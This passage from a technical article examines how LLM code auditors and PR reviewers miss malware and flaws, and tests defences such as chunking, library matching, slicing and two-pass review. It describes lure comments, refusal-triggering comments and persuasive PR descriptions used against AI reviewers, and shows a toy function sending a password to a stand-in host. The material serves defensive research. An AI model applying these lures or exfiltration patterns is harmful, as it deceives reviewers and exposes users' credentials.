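A model can get worse at finding vulnerabilities long before a file fills its context window. Sovrano, Bauer and Bacchelli (2025), in *Large Language Models for In-File Vulnerability Localization*, gave six models 794 real files with known flaws of three types: cross-site scripting, SQL injection and path traversal. The models found fewer flaws in larger files, and fewer of the flaws that were far from the start of a file.

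Real files differ in many ways, so the researchers then tested the same flaws at different positions and file lengths. For each type of flaw, they took five examples and placed each one at every 500-character step in files of 4,000, 8,000, 16,000 and 25,000 characters, filling the rest with functions from the same file or repository. They ran each of the 530 combinations per type five times. In the longer files, the models did worst on flaws near the end, a pattern that Sovrano and colleagues call "lost in the end". When the models pointed to the wrong line, it was usually near the start.

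The largest of these files took up only about 5% of GPT-4o's context window, so the models were overlooking code they had received. However, the task was harder than judging whether code was flawed, because an answer counted only if it identified a line that the developers had changed to fix the flaw.

Dividing the 794 real files into chunks raised the share of flaws found by an average of 37% in relative terms. GPT-4o found 51.4% of the SQL injection flaws in whole files and 65.0% in chunks of 1,500 characters. The researchers used these same files to pick the best of four chunk sizes for each model and type of flaw, so the improvement on new files would probably be smaller. Chunking also caused more false alarms, mostly because a chunk could contain a database query without the earlier line that made its input safe.

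These models date from 2024, and later results do not support a general rule that models do worst at the end of a file. *Robustness and Reasoning Fidelity of Large Language Models* (2026) placed the code needed to answer a question at the start, middle or end of a long input. Most models did better when it was at the end, particularly with COBOL, an old business programming language. Answering a question about code is a different task from finding an unspecified flaw, which may explain the difference. *SoK* (2025) found no significant effect of position within single functions, and longer functions were easier. An operator therefore has no good reason to assume that the start or end of a file is safe to drop, and should test positions with the model in use.

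Adding relevant code does not reliably help either. *Vulnerability Detection with Interprocedural Context in Multiple Languages* (2026) compared models' verdicts when they were given different amounts of related code from other functions. Only three of 12 comparisons showed a significant difference, and all three favoured less context.

The strongest recent evidence of dilution comes from reviews of proposed changes. In *PRWeaver*, Wang, Cheng and Xie (2026) created 208 working attacks on ten software projects and split each across several pull requests. They mixed these with real, harmless ones and gave them to review tools including Claude Code and GitHub Copilot. The tools detected 16–22% of the attacks when the same review included 24 harmless changes, compared with 50–60% when they reviewed each pull request separately. Splitting an attack without adding harmless changes altered detection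 by at most five percentage points, so splitting explains little of the fall.

This is close to a padding experiment, because the attack stays the same while the harmless material around it grows. Most of the projects were Python web software, so the size of the effect may differ for a bundled JavaScript file. Operators still have reason to keep requests small, even when a model's context window could hold much more.

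### When a partial reading looks like a clean result

If a pipeline keeps only the start of the running example, the model may correctly report that the library code it received is harmless. The software then wrongly records this as a verdict on the whole file, and the operator sees "benign" with no indication that the model read only 6% of the script.

Truncation is also a problem in research. *Chasing Shadows* (2025) reviewed 15 papers on vulnerability detection and found that eight used at least one model with a window of 512 tokens or less. Many vulnerable functions are longer than that, so truncation may have removed the flaw before the model received the code. A published detection rate can therefore include misses caused by truncation rather than by the model's judgement.

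The remedy is to record coverage, which is the share of the code that the model received, and to allow a third verdict:

- "Malicious" if the model flags any part.
- "Benign" only if the model received every part and returned a usable answer for each one.
- "Not fully read" in every other case.

The pipeline should calculate coverage as the share of the whole file, after comment removal, that it sent to the model. It should also list the missing line ranges so that another tool can check them. If one of 30 chunks produces a refusal or an error, the pipeline should label the file "not fully read", even if the other 29 look harmless.

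Noirot Ferrand and colleagues report 100% file coverage with ranking. This means that the scanner returned a verdict for every file, although for the largest ones the model saw only three units. Under the rule above, those files would be "not fully read" unless the model flagged something.

A file in this category needs further analysis, such as a chunked audit or a run in an isolated environment. In the full *CASHEWS* collection, the single-prompt scanner could not process 3.2% of the 4,884 original files (about 156). The share in normal traffic may differ, because half of that collection was malicious. An attacker could overload the second stage by submitting many large harmless files. The operator therefore needs to limit how many unread files each account can have waiting, and should not release unread files automatically when the queue is full.

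## Separating custom code from library code

Much of the code in a large bundle is usually copied from published libraries. A pipeline that identifies the copied code can leave it out, which is safer than guessing which part of the file matters. Cloudflare describes bundles of React (a toolkit for web interfaces) and TON (a blockchain platform) as cover for malicious code. It recommends structural isolation but doesn't explain how to do it or report any tests of it.

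A pipeline can use library matching to identify and remove published code. Alternatively, it can use program slicing, which starts from sensitive operations, such as sending data over a network, and keeps only the code that affects them.

### Matching functions against known releases

Library matching needs a database of official releases. The operator downloads each release from its registry, runs it through the bundling tools that developers commonly use, and stores a fingerprint of every function. The pipeline can then process a submitted script:

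1. Parse the bundle into a syntax tree.
2. Recover the boundaries between modules, the separate source files that the bundler combined. Some bundlers wrap each module in its own function, which makes this easy. Others merge the modules into one scope, so the pipeline has to group functions by which ones refer to each other.
3. Normalise each function so that layout and naming make no difference. Remove comments and spacing, number the local names in order of appearance, and write equivalent expressions in one way. For example, minifiers, which shorten code, often turn `true` into `!0`. Keep strings, numbers, property names and operators, because they affect what the function does.
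4. Compute a cryptographic hash of the result, a short fingerprint that changes if any part of the function changes, and look it up in the database. Do the same for statements outside functions.
5. Set aside the exact matches.
6. Send the auditor everything else, with a short description of each library function that the remaining code calls.

The numbering in step 3 has to restart in each function. If it ran across the whole file, as it does in variable anonymisation, a function's fingerprint would depend on its position in the file. The auditor does not receive this renumbered copy.

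Step 5 needs another condition, because a function can match library code exactly and still behave differently. Suppose a library function sends error reports to an address stored in a variable outside it. An attacker can redirect the reports by changing that variable, without touching the function. The pipeline should therefore set a function aside only if every outside name it uses also refers to matching code from the same release.

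The descriptions in step 6 have to come from the official release, because documentation inside the bundle can contain a lure. Each description should state what the function reads, sends and changes, and which options alter its behaviour. Writing these descriptions for many libraries is a lot of work. *LLM-Assisted Static Analysis for Detecting Security Vulnerabilities* (2024) notes that extracting such specifications by analysing library code takes a lot of resources and is hard to scale. The operator can reduce the work by describing only the functions that submitted scripts call, and reusing each description.

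### The running example after matching

Suppose again that the example script is 6.3 MB, and that its author bundled an unmodified official library. The sizes below are invented to show the calculation:

| Part of the script | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Library code that matches exactly | 6,250 KB | 0 KB |
| Library code that fails to match | 40 KB | 40 KB |
| Code added by the bundler | 9.8 KB | 9.8 KB |
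| `savePreferences` | 0.2 KB | 0.2 KB |
| Descriptions of library calls | 0 KB | 2 KB |
| Total | 6,300 KB | 52 KB |

The auditor would receive less than 1% of the original amount of text, and the harmful function's share of it would rise from about 0.003% to 0.4%. After comment removal and renaming as well, the part that matters would look like this:

```
Library call: sendTo(address, data) sends data to a web address.

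function function1(parameter1) {
  const variable1 = "[string: a claim that the code passed a review]";
  const variable2 = parameter1.password;
  sendTo("https://outside.example", variable2);
}
```

The string with the false claim remains because it is part of the custom logic.

The benefit depends heavily on how much of the library matches. The pipeline would have to set aside at least 94% of the script to fit the rest into a 376 KB context window. If it set aside only 90%, 630 KB would remain, and the operator would still have to rank or chunk the code.

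### Why an unmatched library counts as custom code

A failed match may mean that the developer used a private library, an unusual build tool or an old release missing from the database, or that an attacker hid a payload in a copy of a popular library. The failed match doesn't show which, and the attacker controls every other sign of the code's origin, including the file name, folder, licence notice and version number. If the pipeline accepts any of these as proof, an attacker can keep a payload away from the auditor by labelling it as React. The attacker also controls source maps, which link bundled code to its original sources. The pipeline can use them to help find module boundaries, but it must identify library code by its content.

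Filtering by similarity score is also unsafe. Suppose an attacker adds one function to a library of 5,000. The bundle is still 99.98% identical to the official release, so a tool that sets aside anything above 99% removes the payload along with the library. Matching each function exactly removes the 5,000 originals and leaves the new one, which makes the payload easier to find than in the full bundle. If the attacker alters an existing function instead, the pipeline can show the auditor the official version beside it.

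An exact match only proves that the code is the same as the release, and the release may be malicious. In the ai-sdk-ollama attack, for example, the payload was in the real npm package. If the database had automatically added the compromised release, the pipeline would have set the payload aside in every script that contained it. The operator should audit each release before adding it, and delete its fingerprints if it later turns out to be malicious. For vulnerability detection, the pipeline should also check the names and versions of matched libraries against public lists of known flaws, because the auditor will not read that code.

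### Builds that break the match

Normalisation reverses only some of the changes a minifier makes. Minifiers also merge statements, calculate fixed expressions in advance and replace a call with the body of the function it calls. Each of these changes the syntax tree, so the function's fingerprint no longer matches.

Many bundlers leave out library functions that the program never uses, so a fingerprint of the whole library would almost never match. Fingerprints of single functions still work, unless the bundler has changed the functions too. The operator can store several builds of each release, but with four bundlers and five common settings for each, 1,000 releases would need 20,000 builds.

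A broken match gives the auditor more code to read, so it doesn't hide anything directly. But an attacker can fill the context window again by running a harmless library through an unusual minifier to break matches on purpose. If the code left after matching is too large for the model to read, the file should get the verdict "not fully read", however familiar the library looks.

### Program slicing

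Slicing avoids the need for a database of libraries. It requires a list of sensitive operations, often called sinks, and usually a list of sources, the places where secret or untrusted data enters the program. A backward slice takes the following steps:

1. Find each sink in the program.
2. Find the statements that set the values it uses.
3. Add the conditions that decide whether those statements and the sink run.
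4. Repeat steps 2 and 3 for the statements and conditions just added, until there is nothing new to add.
5. Write out the selected code in its original order.

In the example, the sink is the call to `sendTo`. It uses a fixed address and `variable2`, which comes from the password field. Nothing in this chain uses `variable1`, so the slice leaves it out:

```
function function1(parameter1) {
  const variable2 = parameter1.password;
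  sendTo("https://outside.example", variable2);
}
```

Slicing removed the false claim in the string, which comment removal, renaming and library matching had all left in place. An attacker could keep such a string in the slice by including it in the data the script sends.

A slice can still contain comments. The slicer in *Utilizing Precise and Complete Code Context to Guide LLM* (2024) maps its selection back to lines of source code, and a copied line may end in a comment. Li, Li and colleagues (2025) deliberately keep relevant documentation with each function in *No More Hidden Pitfalls?*, their work on smart contracts, which are programs that run on a blockchain. An auditor that faces hostile authors should slice the pipeline's comment-free copy of the code.

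### Measured results on npm packages

Nguyen and colleagues found that data-flow extracts from npm packages did better than plain chunks. They also tested slices that worked backwards from each sink and included every statement that could run before it, whether or not the statement affected the data.

| Input to the model | Mean tokens | Median tokens | Detection rate | Share of flags that were correct |
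|---|---|---|---|---|
| Whole package, in chunks | 162,920 | 3,594 | 55.5% | 87.1% |
| Slices by order of execution | 379 | 358 | 60.5% | 96.0% |
| Slices by flow of data | 403 | 228 | 72.9% | 96.2% |

Both kinds of slice reduced the average package by more than 99%, but the model detected 12 percentage points more of the malware with slices that followed the data. Shortening the input therefore can't explain the whole improvement. Following the data was also better at leaving out harmless activity. In malicious packages, it kept 73.7% of the lines that mentioned a sensitive function, about the same as the other method (73.4%). In harmless packages, it kept only 9.4% of such lines, compared with 15.9% for the other method.

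These detection rates exclude every package for which the slicer produced nothing. Nguyen and colleagues started with 7,309 packages and kept 2,600 malicious and 3,242 harmless ones after removing damaged archives and packages without sensitive calls. The slicer returned nothing for 1,147 of the malicious packages (44%) and 2,158 of the harmless ones (67%). If a pipeline treated those packages as harmless, its detection rate would fall from 72.9% to about 41%. If it sent them to another tool, that tool would have to examine 57% of the packages they kept.

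An empty slice is therefore weak evidence that a package is safe. Nguyen and colleagues recommend running packages with empty slices in an isolated environment, or decoding them with a model's help and slicing them again. They also excluded packages that contained only a metadata file, although npm metadata can specify commands to run during installation. A pipeline that slices only the JavaScript would miss a payload in those commands.

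### Where a slice stops too early

Building a call at run time is probably the most common way to defeat a slicer. A program can assemble a function's name from pieces of text, or decode hidden code and execute it. The slicer then can't tell which function the program will call, so it may not recognise the sink or may lose track of the data before it gets there. Nguyen and colleagues counted `eval` and similar functions as sinks, which keeps some of the path visible, but they still attribute many of their empty slices to code built at run time.

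Ordinary JavaScript can cause the same problem. Programs often start a task, such as a download, and supply another function to run when it finishes. Nguyen and colleagues warn that this style frequently breaks links in the data-flow graph, so a source and a sink that belong together look unconnected. *Utilizing Precise and Complete Code Context to Guide LLM* adds links that standard code graphs lack, covering calls, structure and variables.

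Slicing also depends on the list of sensitive functions. The npm experiment used 256 entries in seven groups, drawn largely from known attacks, so a payload that relies on an unlisted function may never enter a slice. Tools also limit how far they search. Li and colleagues include called functions to a depth of three, which keeps the input short but would leave out a sensitive operation four calls away. The npm slicer stopped after three minutes per package, a limit an attacker could exploit by making the code slow to analyse. In malware triage, a slice that ends at a limit or an unresolved call should never be enough for a "benign" verdict.

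### Auditors built on extracted facts

Some designs go further and make slices or other extracted facts the auditor's main input. *LLMxCPG* (Lekssays, Mouhcine and colleagues, 2025) used two models to look for memory-related flaws. The first model read the code and wrote a query that selected a suspicious path through it. Software ran the query and collected the statements that affected the path, and the second model judged the resulting slice. The slices contained no comments by design and were 68% to 91% shorter than the original code.

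The short slices did not make the verdicts reliable. On 57 flaws published in 2025 and the fixed version of each, the system detected 64.4% of the flaws, but only 59.2% of its flags were correct. If it had flagged every sample, 50% would have been correct. Choosing the slice is part of the difficulty. Three security experts examined the queries behind 25 wrong verdicts and found that 40% targeted a different type of flaw and another 32% left out essential context. The first model also reads the unsliced code, so misleading text there could influence what it selects, even if comments are removed from the second model's input.

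Lekssays and colleagues also tested slices after adding code that never runs. In one dataset, detection fell from 18 of 40 flaws to 13. In another, it fell from 95.3% to 62.8%, but the model's figures imply that it had also flagged about three-quarters of the harmless samples before the change. Irrelevant code can therefore still affect a model that reads slices. The researchers added the code after slicing, so the experiment doesn't show whether the slicer would have removed it.

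In *Trace Gadgets*, Mächtle, Loose and colleagues (2025) start from Java bytecode, the compiled form of a program, which contains no comments. Their tool follows each path from user input to a sensitive operation, drops unrelated statements such as logging, and merges the rest into one function. In their example, the variables also have neutral names, such as `v1` and `v2`. The resulting code was 28% to 34% shorter than earlier representations, and two existing detectors had 29% to 38% lower false positive rates when they used it. JavaScript usually arrives as source text, so an auditor for the example script would have to get the same result from a syntax tree.

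Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *LLMDFA*, ask the model much narrower questions:

1. The model writes a small program that searches syntax trees for sources and sinks. It works from the operator's specification and sample programs, so text in the audited file cannot influence it.
2. The model reads one function at a time and decides whether a value on one line can affect a value on another. Software joins the answers into longer paths.
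3. The model writes a script that gives each path's conditions to a solver, which works out whether they can all be true at once. If they can't, the path is impossible and the system discards it.

Separating custom code from library code keeps whole files out of the prompt, but the model still reads the text of individual functions. Wang and colleagues removed comments from one of their test sets because the comments revealed the answers. The design does not remove comments, so an operator who expects misleading ones has to add that step.

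They also tested the system with GPT-3.5 on 80 known data flows in real Android malware. The published percentages correspond to these counts:

| Method | Flows found, out of 80 | False reports |
|---|---|---|
| LLMDFA | 49 | 16 |
| The same model, asked directly | 20 | 26 |
| CodeFuseQuery | 35 | 13 |

Dividing the task more than doubled the number of flows found and reduced false reports. The test measured how well each method traced data, which is only part of deciding whether a program is malicious. The system found 71.7% of 138 known vulnerabilities in JavaScript packages, and about 92.5% of its reports were correct.

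CodeFuseQuery applies fixed rules to the syntax tree and uses no language model, so reassuring text in the code cannot sway its results. Wang and colleagues attribute its misses mainly to program features that it handles poorly, such as global variables and arrays. Gajjar (2025) argues that syntax trees and graphs of execution order show local structure but miss wider connections and intent.

A neural network that reads a syntax tree has less protection than a fixed rule, because the tree still contains names and strings. For example, Yefet and colleagues attacked the code2vec network, which works from paths through a syntax tree, by changing one variable name.

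Newer systems combine extracted facts with a model's judgement. *VulWeaver* (Cao, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the model slices with relevant definitions, declarations and examples of use. Its reported F1 score on a set of Java vulnerabilities is 0.75, 15% better than earlier methods based on language models. The system also found 26 real flaws in nine Java projects, and developers confirmed 15 of the flaws. But VulWeaver uses a model to help build the dependency graph where fixed rules are inaccurate, so misleading text could affect the slice before the auditor sees it. Selecting relevant code also doesn't by itself remove its comments.

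*VulTriage* (2026) turns a program's syntax tree, order of execution and data flow into a short description in ordinary language. Such a description can keep misleading text from the auditor only if it replaces the source code in the prompt and the software that writes it doesn't copy misleading names and strings.

### Flaws between custom and library code

Some flaws exist in neither the custom code nor the library alone. Wu, Liu and colleagues, in *Enhancing Vulnerability Detection via Inter-procedural Semantic Completion*, point out that many vulnerabilities span several functions, and that detectors lose important information when they judge one function without the functions it calls. Library matching can create the same problem. Suppose a custom function displays a visitor's comment on a web page:

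```
showText(comment.text, { raw: true });
```

The library's `showText` normally makes user input safe to display, but `raw: true` turns this protection off and lets a visitor's comment run as code in other people's browsers. The description of `showText` needs to include what the `raw` option does, because an auditor who reads only that the function displays text has no reason to object.

Libraries can also call custom code. For example, a script may pass a library a function to run whenever someone submits a form. If the library is removed, the auditor may mistake that function for dead code, as it may with a renamed entry point, unless the description includes when the library calls functions passed to it.

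Custom code can replace a library function while the program runs. The bundled library still matches the official release, but its description is no longer accurate. The pipeline should look for custom code that assigns new values to library objects. If it finds any, it should send the auditor the affected library code in full and mark the description as unreliable.

### What the cost would depend on

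How many flaws isolation would miss depends partly on the task. Like comment removal and renaming, isolation probably does less harm in malware triage, where the payload is often a self-contained piece of custom code. In vulnerability detection, more flaws are likely to depend on how a developer uses a library, so the quality of the descriptions matters more.

The number of detections lost by isolating custom code depends on where the harmful code is. If every malicious script in a test has its payload in a separate custom function, library matching will appear to lose no detections. The test should therefore also include altered libraries, compromised releases and flaws in how custom and library code interact. For each detection lost after isolation, the operator should check whether the pipeline removed the harmful code itself or only the context that made it recognisable. If it removed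 the code, the matching or slicing rule needs to change, but if it removed only the context, a better description of the library call may be enough.

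## Checking the verdict against evidence outside the comments

Removing comments, names and library code keeps some lures away from the model, but it also removes honest information. An operator can instead leave the text in place and limit how far it can change the verdict. Thornton tested three ways of doing this on four commercial models, using the same samples as for comment removal:

| Measure | Detection rate | Earlier misses recovered | Requests per sample | Estimated gain, in points |
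|---|---|---|---|---|
| Two passes, with and without comments | 96.1% | 20 of 57 | 2 | +2.2 |
| Static-analysis findings as hints | 96.9% | 27 of 57 | 1 | +2.9 |
| Scan for suspicious comments | 95.1% | 0 of 57 | 1 | +1.4 |

The last column corrects for the easier mix of samples after each defence, and covers the three models with complete enough results. The same estimate for comment removal is −0.2 points. The scan recovered none of the 57 misses, so its apparent gain of 1.4 points suggests how much of the other gains could be due to chance or a remaining mismatch in the samples. Hints beat two passes by 0.8 points overall, only about nine detections in 1,160 runs.

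### Telling the model to distrust comments

The simplest measure is to add an instruction to the operator's prompt. Thornton told the models to treat comments, docstrings and other inline documentation as untrusted and to base their analysis only on the executable code.

The commercial models had 14 induced misses (flaws they missed only with misleading comments) with the plain prompt and four with the distrustful prompt. If each of these 18 misses had been equally likely under either prompt, a split at least this uneven would occur about 3% of the time. The true probability is probably higher because the misses were not independent (three of the 14 were on the same sample). The count also excludes detections gained with the comments, which Thornton does not report for the distrustful prompt. The instruction may well help against fixed comments, but this evidence is weak.

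A more elaborate prompt did worse, with ten induced misses. It told the models to list where data enters the program and where the program uses it, then trace the paths between them. Thornton suggests that this method kept the models from noticing flaws that don't fit it, such as race conditions, in which the result depends on the timing of two operations.

Thornton's wording also leaves a gap because it covers only comments. In the running example, the string claiming that the code passed a review and the friendly names are both part of the executable code, so the instruction doesn't apply to them. A better instruction would cover text anywhere in the file and allow the model to use it as a lead, but never as a reason to clear the code. Even then, the model would still read the text, and nothing outside the model would enforce the rule.

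### Two passes, with and without comments

In a two-pass review, the pipeline sends the original file in one request and a comment-free copy in another. Thornton counted a flaw as found if either pass found it. Under this rule, a comment can add a flag but can't remove one, because the second pass doesn't see it. The first pass keeps the benefit of honest warnings and of lures so blatant that they arouse suspicion. Most of Cloudflare's models flagged more scripts with 1,000 added comments, and two passes would keep those extra detections.

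Ordinary software should combine the two verdicts, because if a model makes the final decision from both reports, a false claim repeated in one of them could still mislead it.

Part of the gain may come simply from reviewing the code twice. For the three models in the estimate above, average detection was about 94% with or without comments, and 96.3% when a detection in either pass counted. The two passes evidently missed somewhat different flaws, but two runs on the same version might do so as well. Thornton did not test this, though an operator can do so by sending the comment-free copy twice and comparing the result with that of one pass with comments and one without.

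Flagging a file when either pass flags it can also raise the false positive rate. If each pass wrongly flags 5% of harmless files, the combined rate is 5% when both always make the same mistakes, 9.75% (1 − 0.95²) when their mistakes are independent, and 10% when they never make the same mistake. An honest comment explaining why some unusual code is safe can't prevent a false alarm from the comment-free pass, because the comment has been removed. Thornton tested only vulnerable code, so the size of the increase in false positives is unknown.

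Requiring both passes to flag a file would reduce false alarms, but a lure that fooled the first pass would then be enough to clear the file. The operator gets more from treating disagreement as information:

| With comments | Without comments | Reasonable response |
|---|---|---|
| Flagged | Flagged | Flag the file |
| Cleared | Flagged | Flag it in malware triage; in vulnerability detection, check the claim that may have changed the verdict |
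| Flagged | Cleared | Check whether the comments describe a real flaw or contain a lure |
| Cleared | Cleared | Clear the file, if the model received all of it |

Some disagreements will come from ordinary variation between runs, so the operator needs to know how often two identical requests disagree before drawing strong conclusions from a disagreement.

In July 2026, Wu and Nita-Rotaru tested defences against comments that had been revised in response to the auditor's verdicts. Instructions helped little, and a separate pass without comments helped on some systems. Filtering before the audit worked best, but they did not revise the comments again to get past the filter.

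### Static-analysis findings as points to verify

A static analysis tool can give the model specific findings to check instead of an open search. The pipeline runs the tool first, puts each finding in the prompt with the type of problem and the line number, and asks the model whether the finding is correct. In the running example, a rule that follows data through the syntax tree could report that line 4,004 reads a password field and line 4,005 sends the value to an outside address, regardless of the comment or the variable's name.

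Hints had the highest detection rate in Thornton's comparison and needed only one request per sample, but the benchmark favoured them. Thornton had confirmed that static analysis tools could detect every flaw in it. In real code, a tool will miss some flaws, and the model will get no hints about those.

The keyword scoring may also have favoured hints, because a hint often supplies the keyword. A model that dismissed a suspected SQL injection as a false alarm could still get credit for finding it. Even so, 30 of the 57 earlier misses remained. For those flaws, either the hint was missing or the model's answer didn't name the problem.

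Hints can also do harm, as the false assurances in *Trusting the Tool* did. The pipeline should therefore pass on what the tool found but not tell the model when the tool found nothing, because the tool may have no rule for the flaw. Shahriar and colleagues found that telling a model that an automated analysis has marked code vulnerable can make it flag more harmless code. Neutral wording may reduce this effect, and asking the model to look for other problems may keep it from stopping at the listed findings.

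The model should verify findings on a copy of the code without comments. Otherwise, a comment that denies the flaw can lead it to reject a correct finding. The operator may not want to let the model dismiss serious findings at all.

### Scanning comments for suspicious patterns

Thornton's comment scan used about 30 search patterns. When one matched, the pipeline kept the comment and added a warning to the model's instructions. This recovered none of the 57 misses. Thornton's explanation is that the models had missed them because the flaws were hard to find, so a warning about the comments did not help.

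That makes the experiment a poor test of the scan's main purpose, countering comments that actually change verdicts. Real lures show the scan's limits more clearly. English patterns would not match the parts of Cloudflare's notice that were in other languages, and an attacker can reword a claim until no pattern fits. A scan takes almost no compute and can catch crude or repetitive lures, but a lack of matches doesn't show that a file is safe.

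### Asking about one kind of abuse

Cloudflare recommends replacing a general question about abuse with a specific one, such as whether the script is a phishing page or a proxy. It reports that this gives better results but publishes no measurements. A specific question probably helps because it directs the model to particular evidence, such as a login form that sends its contents off the site in the case of phishing. A general assurance that the code is harmless is also less relevant to a specific question than to a general one.

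The closest measured evidence comes from Alexopoulos and colleagues, who varied the operator's instructions on vulnerable and fixed files. Telling Claude 3.5 Haiku that a named type of flaw was present raised its detection rate from 68.4% to 83.4%, but lowered the share of fixed files it cleared from 31.6% to 18.0%. Suggesting only that the code might contain vulnerabilities lowered detection to 43.7%. The other five models already flagged nearly everything, so their detection had little room to rise. These prompts were statements, which probably pushed the model harder towards a flag than questions would have. A neutral question may cause fewer false alarms, but the operator has to test it on harmless code.

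Asking several specific questions again creates repeated chances for error. Cloudflare's 100 scripts fell into four categories, so four questions would cover them. If each question led to false flags on 2% of harmless scripts and the mistakes were independent, 1 − 0.98⁴, or about 7.8%, would get at least one false flag. The list of questions also has to be complete. If it covered only proxies, file hosting and streaming, the model could answer all three questions correctly and the example script, which steals passwords, would still get through. A final general question lets the model report abuse that the list doesn't cover.

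### Checking safety claims against the code

Cloudflare also recommends comparing safety claims with what the program does, again without a test or a detailed procedure. A pipeline could do it this way:

1. Collect the safety claims in comments, strings and documentation. Record only the type of claim and its location.
2. Turn each claim into a question about behaviour, such as whether the code sends data to an outside address.
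3. Answer the question from a comment-free copy, using fixed rules or a slice where possible.
4. Mark the claim as supported, contradicted or impossible to check.

A model can do the first step, but it should choose from a fixed list of claim types, because a free-form summary may repeat the misleading claim in new words and pass it to the next step.

A supported claim can reduce suspicion, but only on the point it covers. A claim that nobody can check should count for nothing. In the running example, the string contains a claim that the code passed a review, which an auditor cannot check from the code. The function's name implies that it saves preferences, which an auditor can check and which is inconsistent with sending a password to another site. Such a contradiction is evidence of deceit in malware triage, but in vulnerability detection it may only mean that a developer changed the code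 and forgot to update the comment.

Some claims mix facts with judgement. According to the notice in Cloudflare's script, for example, the script made no malicious network requests. Software can list the requests, but somebody still has to decide whether they are malicious.

Reviewers sometimes make this comparison unprompted. In one test, Alexopoulos and colleagues gave Claude Code a change that removed a network protection. Claude Code accepted the change when the description was neutral. When the change was described as adding the protection, Claude Code noticed the contradiction and rejected it.

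*From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes PRGuard, a review system that makes the check a separate stage. PRGuard first proposes a specific vulnerability in a pull request, then looks for evidence in the repository for each fact the vulnerability depends on. It relies only on the repository as it was before the change. It excludes even new or edited tests, because an attacker can write a test that builds in the same false assumption as a comment.

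The separate stage is meant to prevent reviews that reach the right verdict for the wrong reason. In one case, a change let users reach another project's data because the code never checked which project a submitted identifier belonged to. A reviewer blocked the change over an unrelated problem with how the page displayed secrets, so fixing only that problem would have left the real flaw in place. On 12 previously unknown flaws in real projects, PRGuard and the commercial reviewer CodeRabbit each blocked ten changes. PRGuard identified and proved the actual flaw in all ten, while CodeRabbit did so in four. The comparison favours PRGuard because it had originally found those 12 flaws. On 31 other malicious changes, PRGuard blocked about as many as CodeRabbit and, when running on a DeepSeek model, identified 1.38 times as many of the actual flaws. The cases came from project histories, security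 advisories and PRGuard's own discoveries, so these results measure diagnosis more than resistance to misleading text.

Models often give wrong reasons for correct verdicts. Alexopoulos and colleagues checked the justification for every correct flag that their six models gave to vulnerable files. Under neutral instructions, the share of justifications that were wrong ranged from 46% (Claude Opus 4.5) to 71% (Claude 3.5 Haiku), but those flags still counted towards the detection rate. *SEVRA-BENCH* records how many of a reviewer's rejections rest on explicit security reasoning. An operator who measures only verdicts could miss a lure that hides the real flaw if the model still flags the file for something else.

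### When the auditor returns no verdict

All of these checks assume the model gives an answer. With 1,000 added comments, two of the frontier models Cloudflare tested sometimes returned garbled text or a refusal instead. Cloudflare warns that if an automated defence blocks a script only when it receives a clear "malicious", an attacker could disable it this way without persuading the model of anything.

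Attackers have tried to make AI scanners refuse to analyze code. In September 2026, WeLiveSecurity's *GuardBreaker* described a script that the Russia-aligned group UAC-0099 had used against a target in Ukraine to download and install further malware. One comment in the script contained an unrelated request for dangerous weapons information. ESET, the security company behind the site, believes the comment was meant to trigger an AI scanner's safety rules and stop it before it reached the malicious part. ESET gives no evidence that this worked on any particular scanner. A search for reassuring comments would have missed this comment because it didn't contain any claim that the code was safe.

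A refusal or a malformed answer should not count as a pass, because neither shows that the code is harmless, and the file's author may have caused either one. If the pipeline releases files without a verdict, an attacker only has to stop the model from answering, which may be easier than convincing it that the code is harmless.

The pipeline can handle a missing verdict in the same way as a file that the model has not fully read:

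1. Accept only answers that match the required form exactly, and record everything else as "no verdict".
2. Retry with a comment-free copy, which will no longer contain a trigger that was in a comment.
3. If that fails, use a different model or a tool that doesn't depend on a language model.
4. Hold the file until one of these gives a usable result or a person has examined it.

The software should limit retries, because if it keeps asking until it gets "benign", random variation will eventually clear some malicious files. It should also keep a "malicious" answer from any stage, even if a later attempt returns "benign".

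Security tools and scientific software can contain text that triggers a safety filter, so a refusal doesn't prove that code is malicious. But if the model refuses the original and responds normally to a copy without comments, the comments probably caused the refusal, and a person should review them.

The measured detection rate also has to account for missing verdicts. Suppose an auditor receives 100 malicious scripts, flags 72, clears eight and refuses 20. It detects 90% of the 80 scripts it gave a verdict on, but 72% of all 100. If the pipeline lets refused files through, the 72% figure applies. If it holds them, only eight scripts get through, but the operator needs the capacity to examine the 20 refused scripts. The operator will also have to examine any harmless files the auditor refuses, so the test should count those as well.

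### Text outside the source files

Cleaning the source files doesn't protect an auditor that also reads a change's description or the project's documentation. Alexopoulos and colleagues tested this on two real review tools, Claude Code and CodeRabbit. Their paper is due to appear at ICSE 2027, a software engineering conference, according to a post by its co-author Spinellis (2026). They submitted changes that reintroduced 33 known flaws projects had already fixed, 17 to Claude Code and 16 to CodeRabbit. Assurances written to a fixed formula didn't really help the attacker, but when the researchers revised the text after each rejection, 32 of the 33 changes eventually got through.

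They then removed the description from each of the 32 accepted changes and had the tools review them again. If a change was still not rejected, they also removed its commit message and comments and repeated the review.

| Text removed | Claude Code: still accepted | CodeRabbit: still accepted |
|---|---|---|
| Description | 4 of 17 | 9 of 15 |
| Description, commit message and comments | 1 of 17 | 3 of 15 |

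Claude Code had also accepted one change with no persuasive text, and CodeRabbit had accepted three. Alexopoulos and colleagues trace CodeRabbit's three to a bug in the product, which they reported to the company. They count detection as restored in every case that persuasive text had affected.

Some of the improvement in the first row is chance. Repeating the reviews without removing anything produced the same acceptances 76% of the time in Claude Code and 66% in CodeRabbit, so repetition alone should overturn about four of Claude Code's 17 acceptances and five of CodeRabbit's 15. Removing the description overturned 13 in Claude Code and six in CodeRabbit. The description apparently influenced Claude Code strongly, while CodeRabbit's results changed clearly only after the commit message and comments were also removed.

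The experiment didn't test removing comments alone. Claude Code's results suggest that this would often have failed to protect it, because the text that influenced it was in the description. The experiment also included no harmless changes, so it doesn't show how many of these a reviewer would reject without their descriptions.

Leaving a description out of the prompt may not be enough, because some reviewers collect their own context. In these tests, Claude Code could open files, run Git commands and search the web. Git stores a project's history, including commit messages, so an agent with access to it can read text that the pipeline left out. An agent given a copy with the comments removed can still read them if it can open the original.

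Hiding the whole history would remove useful evidence, though. An old commit message may show that a line fixes a security flaw, which is a good reason to question a change that deletes the line. In another test, the reviewer rejected a change partly because it broke the project's written security policy. The pipeline can keep both kinds of evidence by using PRGuard's boundary between old and new material. It can let the reviewer read messages and documents from before the change, and withhold those that came with the change or treat them as untrusted. If the change edits the security policy, the reviewer should use the old version. This is rarely possible in malware triage, because a stranger's new package has no trusted earlier version.

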